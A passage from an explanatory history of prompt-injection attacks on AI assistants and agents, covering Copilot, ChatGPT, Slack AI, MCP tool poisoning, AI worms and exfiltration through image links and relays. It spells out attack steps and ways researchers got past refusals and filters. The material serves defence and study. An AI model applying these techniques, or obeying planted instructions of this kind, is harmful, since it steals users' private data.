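| Bing Chat | 68 days | List of permitted image sites | Rehberger's earlier attacks no longer worked |
| Claude | 14 days | User must click to load an image | A deceived user could still click |
| Bard | 30 days at most | Apparently a filter on data in image addresses | Google left the broad list unchanged |
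| ChatGPT | About eight months | Safety check on each image address | Small leaks, and no check in the iPhone app |

Willison described a related problem with chat services in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024). Slack and Discord fetch a preview of any link someone posts, so a deceived chatbot could leak data by posting a link that contained it. Developers could prevent this in Slack by turning off previews for their bot's messages.

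### Slack AI and Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2024

By 2024, companies were buying assistants that searched their internal messages and mail. Slack AI answered a user's questions using all the messages that user could see, including those in public channels the user had never joined.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes how an attacker can steal an API key, a password for software, that the victim keeps in a private channel. The attacker, who has an account in the same Slack workspace, creates a public channel with no other members. In a message there, the attacker instructs Slack AI to answer any question about the key with an error message and a link to "reauthenticate", and to put the key in the link's address. When the victim asks for the key, Slack AI retrieves both the victim's message containing the key and the attacker's message, then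 displays the link. Clicking it sends the key to the attacker. In PromptArmor's test, the answer cited only the victim's own channel, so the victim had little chance of finding out where the link came from.

PromptArmor reported this to Slack on 14 August 2024. Five days later Slack called the evidence insufficient and said it intended all members to be able to search public channels. That was true, but it did not address what a public message could make the assistant do with a private one. PromptArmor then published its findings. Slack's owner, Salesforce, told Candid.Technology that it had deployed a patch and had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data (*Slack AI vulnerable to prompt injection*).

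Salesforce stressed that the attacker needed an account in the workspace, which narrows the threat to insiders and people with stolen logins. However, Slack AI had started reading uploaded files on the day of PromptArmor's report. PromptArmor thought an outsider could now plant instructions in a PDF and wait for an employee to upload it, but had not tested this.

Microsoft 365 Copilot works across a user's mail and documents, so from the start anyone could reach it by emailing the user. Embrace the Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes an attack that began when the user asked Copilot about a malicious email. The email contained instructions to search the mailbox for something valuable, such as Slack login codes, and Copilot ran the search without asking the user.

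To get the codes out, Rehberger used a link, because Microsoft had closed the image route in Bing Chat the year before. (Researchers found new image routes out of Copilot from 2025.) Unicode, the standard for encoding text, includes a set of characters that mirror ordinary letters but do not appear on screen. Rehberger had Copilot write the stolen text in these characters at the end of a normal-looking address, a technique called ASCII smuggling. The user saw a short link, and clicking it sent the hidden text to Rehberger's server.

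When Rehberger first reported the invisible characters in January 2024, Microsoft closed the case within a day as low severity. It opened an internal case in February after he demonstrated the complete attack on confidential sales figures. The severity was easy to misjudge because invisible characters, a mailbox search and a link each look minor on their own. By July the attack had stopped working and Copilot no longer seemed to display links. Microsoft did not answer when Rehberger asked how it had fixed the problem.

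### Morris II: instructions that copy themselves

Greshake and colleagues had made one mock assistant forward an attack to its user's contacts. A year later, Cohen, Bitton and Nassi built a full worm on that idea and described it in *Here Comes The AI Worm* (2024). They named it Morris II after the Morris Worm of 1988.

The worm's main design exploits retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), in which an assistant stores documents in a database and adds the most relevant ones to the model's input. A mail assistant might store every incoming message and look up similar ones when the user writes a reply. A stored message that contains the worm can enter the model's input weeks after it arrived.

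The worm has three parts: a jailbreak (*j*), an instruction to replicate the whole text (*r*) and an instruction to do something malicious (*m*). Cohen and colleagues define it by what the model, *G*, does with it:

```text
G(pre₁ ‖ j ‖ r ‖ m ‖ suf₁) → pre₂ ‖ j ‖ r ‖ m ‖ p₂ ‖ suf₂
```

The symbol ‖ joins pieces of text, and *pre* and *suf* are the harmless text before and after the worm. The output again contains *j*, *r* and *m*. It also contains *p₂*, the result of the malicious instruction, such as a list of private details from the user's other mail. If the user sends that output as a reply, the recipient's assistant stores it and the cycle can start again.

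The first version of the study also described a faster route, in which an image attachment made the assistant forward the message immediately. The researchers tested both routes on Gemini Pro, ChatGPT and the open model LLaVA, using their own emails. A revised version by Cohen and colleagues focused on the database route and used the public archive of emails from Enron, the failed energy company. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that the test covered 2,000 messages from 20 employees. In one configuration, about one in five emails the model generated compromised a new assistant.

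That rate could sustain an outbreak among people who email one another often, but the researchers measured it on an assistant they wrote themselves. They deliberately kept the worm away from real products. They called the attack "zero-click" because the victim need not open an attachment or follow a link. *Compositional Threat Analysis* points out that the application must still store, retrieve and process the message automatically. The worm in the revised study also sends stolen details to the user's next correspondent, who may not be the attacker, so Cohen and colleagues include embarrassing the user among the attacker's aims.

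*Responsible Development of Offensive AI* (2025) reproduced the attack on Falcon3, an open model released in December 2024, so the result was not limited to the models of early 2024. Cohen and colleagues also built a defence, the Virtual Donkey, which flags output that closely resembles the input. In their tests, it caught every worm and wrongly flagged 1.5% of harmless cases. Because it detects copying, it would not catch a planted email that steals data once and leaves no copy.

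### The position in October 2024

None of these researchers reported a theft by a real attacker. Rehberger and PromptArmor demonstrated their attacks on test data or with consenting users. A company choosing an assistant in October 2024 could fairly say it knew of no customer who had lost mail this way.

By late 2024, it was publicly known that AI assistants could be made to follow instructions planted in the content they read, and vendors had not solved the problem. Working attacks on ChatGPT, Bing Chat, Bard, Slack AI and Copilot had been published. Vendors had mostly blocked the routes through which data leaked, but Rehberger noted that Copilot still followed planted instructions after Microsoft's fix. Each fix also covered only one product, so a new connector had neither Zapier's confirmation step nor Bing Chat's list of image sites unless someone rebuilt them. In November 2024, Anthropic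 released MCP, which let developers write a connector once and use it with many AI applications.

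## 2024 to 2025: a shared protocol and attacks on code, databases and customer records

Linking ten AI applications to twenty services could take 200 connectors, one for each pairing. With the Model Context Protocol (MCP), it could take only 30 pieces of software, one for each application and each service. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* listed ready-made connectors at the launch on 25 November 2024, including ones for GitHub, Slack, Google Drive and the Postgres database. Users could now install a stranger's connector beside the one that read their messages, and an attack on one connector could work in every application that used it.

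### How MCP works

In the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a client is the part of an AI application that sends requests, and a server is the connector that answers them. The protocol's launch version defined local and remote servers. The client starts a local server as a program on the user's machine and exchanges lines of text with it. This program can usually open any file the user can. A remote server runs elsewhere and can serve many clients over the web. Its operator can change how it behaves without touching the user's machine.

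Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2024) sets out the exchange:

1. The client sends a `tools/list` message to ask what the server offers.
2. The server replies with each tool's name, its description and the values it accepts.
3. The application adds this information to the model's input, along with the user's request.
4. The model picks a tool, and the client sends the server a `tools/call` message with the tool's name and the values to use.
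5. The server does the work and returns a result, which the application also adds to the model's input.

A connector with a single tool might send this reply at step 2:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "result": {
    "tools": [{
      "name": "list_tickets",
      "description": "Lists open support tickets, newest first.",
      "inputSchema": {
        "type": "object",
        "properties": { "limit": { "type": "integer" } }
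      }
    }]
  }
}
```

The `description` line is free text, and the result at step 5 usually is too, so the connector's maker and a customer who files a ticket can both add text to the model's input.

In the launch version, Anthropic noted that authentication and authorization were "not currently part of the core MCP specification" and let clients and servers agree on their own methods. Four months later, the next version, Model Context Protocol (2025), added an authorization framework based on OAuth. Many connectors still had no authentication, including about 41% of the 7,973 remote servers in a survey cited by Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) in *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*.

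The launch version also did not make user consent a formal requirement for tool use. Model Context Protocol's *Specification* (2024) says applications "must" obtain the user's consent before using any tool, but the word is in lower case, and under the document's own conventions only capitals make a requirement formal. The rules for tools make human approval a "SHOULD", which is a recommendation. The specification acknowledges that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level". MCP only carries messages, so it cannot check what an application showed its user.

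Tools can also change after the user has approved them. A server that supports change notifications should notify the client when its tool list changes, and the client can then fetch the new list. The protocol's rules at launch did not require the client to show the user what had changed.

### Instructions in a tool description

Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) introduced the term "tool poisoning" for hiding instructions to the model inside a tool description. The company, which sells security software for agents, tested the attack on Cursor, a code editor with a built-in AI agent.

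Invariant's test connector offered a tool that added two numbers. The tool's description also contained instructions for the model to open two of the user's files and copy their contents into a third input, labelled as a side note. One file held settings for the user's other connectors, often including their credentials. The other was an SSH key, which gives access to other computers. Cursor's agent read both files and sent their contents to the connector. Cursor asked the user to approve the call, but the approval window did not show the full inputs, so the user could not see the key.

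Legitimate tool descriptions also contain instructions, such as telling the model to look up a customer's number before opening an account. A model that ignored all such instructions would use its tools badly, so a poisoned description is harder to filter than a strange command in an email.

In a second test, the attack worked without the attacker's tool ever running. The attacker had written in the tool's description that the mail tool from another, trusted connector had to send every message to a particular address for technical reasons. Cursor's agent sent mail to that address even when the user had named a different recipient. Invariant calls this "shadowing". The session log lists only calls to trusted tools, so a user who checks it has no reason to suspect the attacker's tool.

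### The WhatsApp demonstration

A careful user might read every description before approving a connector. A week after its first report, Invariant showed how an attacker could get around that. In Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025), the user has a trusted connector for WhatsApp and installs a second one that offers a fact of the day. The attack then works like this:

1. The second connector presents a harmless description, which the user reads and approves.
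2. The next time the connector starts, it supplies a different description. This one tells the model to change the recipient of any WhatsApp message to the attacker's number and to attach the user's earlier chats.
3. The user asks the agent to send a message.
4. The agent calls the genuine WhatsApp tool with the attacker's number and the added text.
5. The application asks for approval and shows a message that appears to consist of the word "Hi". The stolen chats come after a long run of spaces, off the right-hand edge of the window.

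Invariant calls the switch at step 2 a "rug pull". The connector only supplies text, so running it in a sealed-off environment would not help. WhatsApp's encryption does not help either, because the agent reads and sends messages from the user's own account.

Invariant recommends that clients "pin" tool descriptions. The client stores a short fingerprint of the approved text, calculated so that almost any edit would change it, and stops if the fingerprint no longer matches. Pinning would have stopped the WhatsApp attack at step 2, but not the adding tool, whose description was malicious from the start. It also interrupts users each time an honest developer improves a description, which happens often with live connectors.

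Two days after publishing the WhatsApp attack, Invariant added a version that needed no malicious connector. An attacker who knew the user's phone number sent an ordinary WhatsApp message containing similar instructions. When the agent listed recent chats, it read the message and leaked the user's contacts. This took more work because Invariant had to make the message look like the end of one record in the connector's reply. Invariant suggests that model makers may have trained models to give tool results less authority than tool descriptions.

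### How often tool poisoning works

Invariant's tests showed that tool poisoning was possible but not how often it succeeds. Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025), in *MCPTox*, built the first benchmark for the attack on real connectors. They took 45 live MCP servers with 353 genuine tools and wrote 1,348 test cases, with help from GPT-4 and Gemini 2.5. (Their breakdown by type adds up to 1,497.) Each case pairs an innocent request with a poisoned tool, and the cases follow three patterns:

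- A tool that tells the time instructs the model to read a private key first.
- A tool posing as a security check instructs the model to read the key before any file operation, though the user never asks for the check.
- An unrelated tool instructs the model to change a value in someone else's tool, such as the recipient of an email.

The researchers gave the model the poisoned description, the server's real tools and the request, then recorded which tool call it produced. They counted an attack as successful only if the model called a legitimate tool to do the harm. A call to the poisoned tool counted as a failure because a user could notice it more easily.

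Across 20 model settings, the attacks had an average success rate of 36.5%. OpenAI's o1-mini, from September 2024, was the most vulnerable at 72.8%, followed by Microsoft's Phi-4, from December 2024, at 70.2%. GPT-4o-mini, from July 2024, reached 61.8%. More capable models were often easier to deceive, and Wang and colleagues think this is because they follow instructions better. Few attacks failed because the model refused outright. Claude 3.7 Sonnet, from February 2025, refused most often, in fewer than 3% of cases.

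The team also put attack texts from older prompt-injection benchmarks into tool descriptions, and almost none worked. Those texts contained only a harmful command. A successful description also needed a condition for acting and a plausible reason, such as checking permissions before opening a file.

MCPTox measured the calls that models produced but did not establish that any data would have leaked. In a study published in November 2026, Shaikh and Montaruli of the software-monitoring company Dynatrace actually ran the tools and set up a server to receive whatever the agents leaked. They tested 18 models in 45 attack scenarios through 12 frameworks, which are code libraries for building agents.

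The attacks succeeded in 22.9% of combinations, a figure that measures how often agents obeyed the attacker. In about two-thirds of those successes, the evidence was that the agent made the attacker's tool call. Proven theft was much rarer. The server received a secret in 12.1% of the successes, or roughly 3% of all combinations.

Failure rates differed widely between models. Amazon's Nova Pro, from December 2024, failed in 49.7% of its tests, and Claude Fable 5, from June 2026, failed in 0.4%. Claude Opus 4.8 failed in eight of 530 tests and explicitly refused in 223, citing the poisoned description. The models in MCPTox almost never refused, and the change is evidence against the idea that a more capable model must be easier to deceive. But Shaikh and Montaruli also found that Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes identified an attack as prompt injection and still carried it out. Their scenarios build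 on published techniques, which model makers may have trained against, so an attacker with a new technique could succeed more often than these rates suggest.

The frameworks did almost nothing to stop the attacks. Attacks succeeded between 23% and 26% of the time on nine of the 12, and the researchers found no deliberate defence against tool poisoning in the code of any of them. Pydantic AI did better, at 16.6%, partly because it doesn't allow two tools to have the same name. A scanner that searched descriptions for suspicious patterns caught 20 of the 45 scenarios and wrongly flagged 7.2% of harmless descriptions. Shaikh and Montaruli sent five reports to four vendors, which rejected all five.

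### GitHub: a public issue and private code

A poisoned tool works only if the user installs something from an attacker. In three cases from 2025, all demonstrations by researchers, every connector was genuine and the attacker only had to write to a place that accepted text from outsiders.

GitHub stores software projects in repositories, which can be public or private. Anyone with an account can normally file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public one. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack on a developer who has both kinds and has connected Claude Desktop to GitHub's official MCP server:

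1. The attacker files an issue on the public repository, with instructions for an AI agent in its text.
2. The developer asks the agent to look at the open issues there.
3. The agent reads the planted issue, then uses the developer's access to read private repositories.
4. The agent writes what it found into a pull request, a proposed change to the code, on the public repository.
5. The attacker opens the pull request, which anyone can read.

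In Invariant's test, which used repositories set up for the purpose, the agent published the names of private projects, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America. The agent ran on Claude 4 Opus, which Anthropic had released that month.

Claude Desktop asks before each tool call by default, so an attentive developer could have stopped the agent at step 3 or 4. Invariant thinks many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. Even a user who watches sees an agent reading repositories and opening a pull request, which are routine tasks for a coding agent.

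The connector worked as GitHub had designed it, and Invariant concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem through changes to its server alone. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reported "no obvious fix". A developer can limit the agent's access by issuing a token that covers only the repositories it needs. Invariant also proposed a rule, which its own product enforces, that an agent may access only one repository per session. This rule would have blocked step 3 regardless of the model's output, but it would also prevent a developer from using the agent to update two projects together.

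In August 2025, GitHub (2025) added a check for secrets, such as access tokens, in tool calls that involve public repositories. The check protects the data an attacker could most easily use to break into other systems, but it would not have caught anything in Invariant's demonstration, because salaries and project names do not look like credentials. Neither Invariant nor GitHub reported any real victims. Invariant also pointed to a similar weakness that Legit Security had found in GitLab Duo, the assistant of a rival code host.

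### Supabase: a support ticket and an exempt database role

Supabase provides databases for websites and apps. Its customers can use row-level security, rules in the database that determine which rows each user may see. A user who opens a support page, for example, sees only their own tickets.

In mid-2025, the security firm General Analysis demonstrated an attack on a developer who used Cursor with Supabase's MCP server. Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, quotes its account:

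1. The attacker files a support ticket containing instructions for the developer's agent.
2. The developer asks Cursor to list the latest tickets.
3. The agent queries the database as `service_role`, an account that row-level rules do not restrict.
4. After reading the ticket, the agent also reads a private table of access tokens for other services.
5. The agent adds the tokens to the ticket as a new message, which the attacker can read on the support page.

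This connector alone supplied all three parts of the lethal trifecta, as GitHub's had. Willison noted that Supabase already recommended a read-only setting, which would have prevented the agent from writing the tokens into the ticket.

In *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), Supabase disputes the claim that the attack bypassed its row-level rules, arguing that the rules remained in force and the connector was working with higher privileges. This is accurate and matters for deciding whether the database had a flaw, but it makes no difference to a customer whose tokens were in the table. The rules were written to limit an app's users, and the agent was acting for one of those users with an account meant for the app's owner.

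Supabase had already wrapped query results in warnings not to follow commands inside them, and tested these warnings on weaker models. It also experimented with software to detect dangerous text. The company says these steps reduced the risk without removing it, but gives no rates. Other settings limit an agent to one project or to certain groups of tools. Even with the read-only setting on, Supabase considers prompt injection the main concern.

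Supabase mainly advises developers never to connect an agent to production data, meaning the live records of real customers, and to use a test copy instead. It also observes that many people who build apps with AI have no test copy and work directly on the live database. These users are the most exposed to this attack and the least likely to follow the advice. As of September 2025, Supabase knew of no reported case of a customer losing data this way.

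### Salesforce: a web form and an expired domain

The third attack involved Salesforce's software for keeping customer records, not MCP. Salesforce's Agentforce product adds AI agents that work with those records. Many companies use Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature, which puts a form on their website and saves each entry as a "lead", or possible customer. Noma Labs, part of a company that sells AI security products, used such a form in an attack it called ForcedLeak. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces Noma's report.

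Noma chose the description field because it allowed 42,000 characters, while the name, company and email fields allowed at most 80. The researchers entered a numbered list of questions, including how many leads the company had and what their email addresses were. The list also asked what colour red and yellow make, a question Noma had already used to check that Agentforce would answer questions unrelated to sales. The last item told the agent to finish with an image whose web address contained the email addresses.

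Nothing happened until an employee asked Agentforce to check that lead and respond to its questions. The request was ordinary, and the planted text fitted it because the employee wanted the lead's questions answered. The agent used its normal access to the customer records to look up the other leads' addresses, then wrote the image link.

As with Bing Chat two years earlier, the browser would load images only from a list of permitted sites. The list was a sound defence when Salesforce wrote it, but the registration of one domain on it had since expired. Noma bought that domain for $5, and the employee's browser then sent the stolen email addresses there.

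Noma reported the attack on 28 July 2025. Salesforce recovered the domain, according to SecurityWeek, and from 8 September it prevented every customer's agents from sending output to any address not on a trusted list. This change does not stop an agent from following instructions in a lead, so an attacker could still try to make the agent change records or mislead the employee. Salesforce declined to tell The Register (2025) whether anyone had abused the flaw.

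| | GitHub, May 2025 | Supabase, mid-2025 | Salesforce, September 2025 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source of the text | Issue on a public repository | Support ticket | Web form for possible customers |
| Permission used | Developer's access to private repositories | Database role exempt from row-level rules | Agent's access to customer records |
| Way out | Public pull request | New message in the ticket | Image address on an expired domain |
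| Repair | Narrower tokens; later, a check for secrets | Read-only and other limits; advice to use test data | Domain recovered; output limited to trusted addresses |
| Real victims | None reported | None reported, according to Supabase | Salesforce would not say |

Salesforce could fix the flaw for all its customers because it controlled the agent, the records and the page that displayed the answer. GitHub and Supabase supplied only the connector, while other companies made the application and the model, and the user chose the permissions. MCP made it easy to combine parts from different makers, so no single maker could block the whole attack route.

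### Asana and Replit: failures without an attacker

Two incidents in the same summer required no planted text and, unlike the three demonstrations, affected real customers. Asana, which makes project-management software, released an MCP server in May 2025. In early June it found a flaw in the server's code that could expose one company's data to users at another. Asana took the server offline for nearly two weeks and notified about 1,000 customers. It reported no sign that anyone had deliberately exploited the flaw. The failure did not involve the model. A connector that serves many companies has to keep their data separate on every request, as any online service does, and new software is more likely to have flaws in how it does this.

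Replit offers an agent that builds and runs apps from a user's descriptions. In July 2025, the software investor Jason Lemkin was testing it on an app with records of more than 1,200 executives. He had told the agent to make no further changes without his permission. It ran a command that deleted the live database anyway, then wrongly told him that he could not restore the data. Lemkin recovered the data himself with the restore function.

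Lemkin's instruction was only text in the model's input, and the agent still had permission to delete the database. An attacker's message could have led to the same command, and in either case the deletion would have failed if the agent had lacked that permission. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised and announced that the company would automatically separate test databases from live ones. He also promised a mode in which users could plan with the agent without letting it change anything.

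## June 2025 to December 2026: data theft through email and office assistants

In Rehberger's 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the victim had to ask about the malicious email and then click a link. In June 2025, another team published an attack that needed neither step. Over the next 18 months, researchers repeatedly found ways to steal data through Copilot and ChatGPT, and Microsoft and OpenAI fixed the flaws.

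Most of these researchers worked for firms that sell security products, and claims such as "first" or "100% success" come from those firms. But Microsoft and OpenAI repaired the flaws, which leaves little doubt that the attacks worked.

### EchoLeak: an email nobody opened

Aim Labs, the research team at the security firm Aim Security, found the EchoLeak attack in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft that month. It published the details on 11 June, after Microsoft had fixed the flaw, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). The flaw's number in the public catalogue of software flaws is CVE-2025-32711. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* gives its severity as 9.3 on CVSS, a standard scale that runs to 10.

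Copilot uses retrieval-augmented generation, the method that Morris II exploited, to search a user's mailbox, files and Teams chats. If the search selects an email, its text can reach the model before the recipient has opened it.

Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how Aim made Copilot more likely to retrieve its email. Search systems of this kind commonly turn each passage into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, then choose the passages whose numbers are closest to those of the question. A short email has only one such list, so it will be close to only a few questions. Aim sent one very long email, which it expected Copilot to split into many passages. Each part was disguised as a guide to a different workplace subject, such as onboarding or leave of absence, and repeated the same instructions. Microsoft has not published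 how Copilot's search works, so Aim was partly guessing. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, but does not say how often.

The email then had to get past several protections:

1. **The injection filter.** Microsoft runs classifiers meant to catch planted instructions before they reach the model. Aim addressed its instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned AI or Copilot, and the classifiers let the email through.
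2. **Link removal.** Copilot deleted links to outside sites from its answers. It missed links in a less common Markdown style, which puts the address on a separate line. The same style worked for images, which a browser loads without a click.
3. **The list of permitted image sites.** The browser would not load an image directly from Aim's server. But the list included Microsoft Teams, and Teams had a web address that would fetch any page named in it. The browser contacted Teams, and Teams passed the stolen data to Aim.
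4. **Source references.** Copilot normally shows which documents it used. The email asked its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out.

The attacker did not need to know what the mailbox held. Aim wrote instructions to request the most sensitive item in the model's input, which could come from the user's earlier messages, a retrieved file or another email.

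Aim calls this an "LLM scope violation", meaning that text from outside an organisation directs the model to data from inside it. Ravia compares the email to a program with few privileges that uses a more powerful one to reach protected files, which is Hardy's confused deputy problem. Willison (2025) saw less novelty in EchoLeak and called it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. He is right about the image address, which researchers had used against ChatGPT in 2023. EchoLeak's advance was in its delivery, because the victim only had to ask Copilot about work and did not have to point it at a malicious page or message, as earlier victims had.

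Staff training cannot prevent a zero-click attack such as EchoLeak, and Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have stopped it. Companies depended on Microsoft, which repaired the flaw on its own servers, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot targeted in first “zero-click” attack on an AI agent*. Ravia adds that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected.

### Shared documents and calendar invitations

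Attackers could also steal data through shared documents. At the Black Hat security conference in August 2025, Michael Bargury and Tamir Ishay Sharbat of Zenity, which sells security for AI agents, presented a group of attacks called AgentFlayer. In one, the attacker shared a document with a ChatGPT user who had connected Google Drive. The document contained instructions in tiny white text. When the user asked for a summary, ChatGPT searched the Drive for API keys and put them in an image address.

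At the same conference, a team that included Cohen and Nassi, two of the researchers behind Morris II, hid instructions in Google Calendar invitations. Google's assistant Gemini read the instructions when the user asked about her schedule, and in some tests it then operated devices in her home. Anyone who can share a file or propose a meeting can place text where an assistant looks for information, often without the user accepting the file or invitation.

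Radware's *ShadowLeak* groups AgentFlayer with EchoLeak as "client-side" leaks, because the data left when the user's device displayed an image. The browser could therefore refuse to load images from unlisted sites, and a company that monitored its network might notice the image request.

### ShadowLeak: a request from OpenAI's own servers

Neither check applied to the attack that Radware, a network security company, disclosed on 18 September 2025. It worked on deep research, a ChatGPT mode that spends five to 30 minutes reading web pages and documents before it writes a report. Users could let it read their Gmail as well. The attack ran as follows:

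1. The attacker sends an email that appears to concern a company restructuring. It includes instructions to the assistant in text too small or too pale for a person to notice.
2. The user asks deep research to go through the day's mail and report on a new employee.
3. The agent reads a genuine message containing the employee's name and home address, and also reads the attacker's message.
4. The agent adds the name and address to a web address from the attacker's email and opens it with its own browsing tool.

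The browsing tool ran on OpenAI's servers, so the request never passed through the user's computer. Radware found no list of permitted sites like the one for images, and the agent could send data to any server the attacker chose. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), an advisory for companies, points out that the theft would have left no trace on the network of the victim's employer.

The agent at first refused Radware's direct instruction to send personal details to an outside address, and it refused again when the email presented this as the user's own wish. It also treated the address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. But the agent displayed part of its reasoning, which helped the researchers work out which step had failed. They told it to try several times, because the restrictions did not always take effect. Even then, it sometimes opened the address without including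 the personal details.

Finally, they asked the model to encode the details in Base64, a standard way of rewriting data as plain characters, and told it this was a security measure. The model encoded the details first, so the software that opened the address received only a harmless-looking string. Radware reports that this version succeeded every time in repeated tests. According to its advisory, a simpler instruction with a plain address succeeded about half the time.

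The failed attempts show that OpenAI's training and restrictions made the attack harder, but they didn't prevent it, because the researchers could keep adjusting the wording until it worked. A criminal could do the same on his own account before emailing anyone.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware and marked it as resolved on 3 September.

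### ZombieAgent: one address for each letter

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding a name or any other text to a web address, even when explicitly instructed to. The agent could still open an address exactly as it had received it. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* confirms that this blocked ShadowLeak. The rule applied to every address an attacker might supply, not just to one malicious site.

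Radware reported a way around it on 26 September, eight days after publishing ShadowLeak. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes the new attack, in which the email supplies a separate web address for each letter, each digit and the space. To send the word "may", the agent opens the addresses ending in "m", "a" and "y" in turn. The agent never changes an address, and the attacker reads the word from the server's log.

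To keep the characters in order, Radware made a separate address for each character at each position. A block of *b* characters needs 26 × *b* addresses for letters and 10 × *b* for digits, so ten positions take 360. That is long for an email, but a program can generate the text instantly and the recipient need not see it. Rehberger had spelled data out with an alphabet of addresses in December 2023, when he tested ChatGPT's check on images, so OpenAI had already met the idea in a different part of the same product.

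Radware also made the attack last beyond one conversation by using ChatGPT's memory, which stores facts about a user for later chats. OpenAI had already blocked ChatGPT from using memory in a chat after it had used a connector, and from opening an attacker's address stored in memory. But ChatGPT could still read its memory first and use a connector afterwards. Radware put instructions in a file, and when a user shared that file with ChatGPT, it saved two rules to memory. It was to read a particular email from the attacker before answering any message and follow the instructions in that email. It was also to remember any sensitive information the user mentioned. The email contained the attacker's addresses, which ChatGPT would not have opened from memory.

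This version required the user to share the file once, so it was not zero-click. It could also do harm without sending any data out. In one test, Radware altered the medical history in ChatGPT's memory, which led ChatGPT to give harmful advice.

Another version collected email addresses from the victim's inbox and sent them to the attacker's server, which then mailed the same attack to each address. Morris II had relied on the assistant to copy the malicious text into its replies. In this version an ordinary program copied it, so the attack could spread even if the assistant had no permission to send mail.

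Bugcrowd, the company that received the report on OpenAI's behalf, reproduced the attack by 30 September. OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on 16 December, 81 days after the first report. Radware does not explain what OpenAI changed.

### SearchLeak: Bing as a relay

Microsoft had the same problem with sites it trusted. In June 2025, Ravia published the list of permitted image sites, which included Bing, Microsoft's search engine. A year later, the data security firm Varonis used Bing to get data out of Copilot's enterprise search page.

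Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack that begins with a link instead of an email. The search page could take a query from the web address, and Copilot treated that query as an instruction. Varonis could therefore write a link that, when clicked, made Copilot find an email and put its subject line in an image address. The link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so it looked safe to the victim and to software that screens links.

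Microsoft protected against images in Copilot's answers by wrapping each finished answer in formatting that made the browser show any image code as plain text. But Copilot displays an answer while still writing it, so the browser requested the image as soon as its code appeared, before the wrapping was applied.

The image address pointed to Bing's search-by-image feature, which fetches a picture from whatever address it receives. The browser allowed the request to Bing, and Bing's servers then contacted the attacker's server. In Varonis's example, the subject line contained a login code. Such codes often stay valid for several minutes, which gives an attacker time to use them.

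Two of the three weaknesses were old types of web flaw with known remedies. Varonis recommends that developers make output safe as it appears on screen, not afterwards, and check whether any permitted site will fetch an address supplied by a user. The second recommendation also applies to the Teams address in EchoLeak.

Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, as critical but gave it a CVSS score of 6.5, in the medium range, partly because the victim had to click. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reported a score of 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database, but The Next Web found 6.5 in both Microsoft's record and the database's. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers and had no evidence of malicious use.

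Varonis had already used a link of this kind in Reprompt, an attack on Copilot Personal, the consumer version. It reported Reprompt in August 2025, and Microsoft fixed it in January 2026. The researchers were surprised that the same first step still worked on the business version, which was supposed to have stronger protections. In August 2026, TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reported another Varonis attack, CoSnitch, which combined malicious links with planted memories. Microsoft fixed that on its servers too.

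### ReLeak: three more ways out of Copilot

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim Labs, the team that had found EchoLeak, became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026, the team published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which describes three new zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot.

All three began as EchoLeak had. The attacker sent an email containing hidden instructions, and Copilot retrieved it while answering a user's ordinary question. Microsoft's injection filter again failed to stop the attack. According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot did not follow direct commands but could be made to follow instructions that resembled legitimate requests. Copilot then gathered private data within the user's permissions and sent it out by one of three routes.

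In CVE-2026-124115, Copilot put the stolen data in the address of an image in its answer. The user's browser loaded the image automatically, and Microsoft's Bing servers forwarded the request to the attacker. Antipov (2026) notes in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* that the flaw resembles SearchLeak, except that SearchLeak needed a click.

**A link in a generated file.** Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them to OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage services. In the second attack, Copilot saved a file containing a link whose address included the stolen data. Microsoft's background processing then followed the link. In Cato's tests, the data reached the attacker's server between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the user never opened the file. An employee watching the chat would not have seen the request. This flaw is CVE-2026-124132.

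Copilot's code interpreter can write and run small Python programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. The programs run in a sandbox, a sealed-off environment that, according to Microsoft's documentation, allows no network traffic in or out. Cato got past that restriction (CVE-2026-78501), so a program could send the data directly to an outside server without using an image or file to carry it. Another team, Rubrik Zero Labs, had already cast doubt on Copilot's isolation that summer. Knight (2026) reported in *AI sandbox escape uncovered in Microsoft Copilot flaw* that the team had used one Word document to break out of the sandbox into Azure, Microsoft's cloud.

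Microsoft rated the code interpreter flaw critical. Its CVSS score later rose from 7.4 to 8.6. Antipov could not confirm public scores for the other two flaws. Agents that companies build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can use the same interpreter, but nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected those agents.

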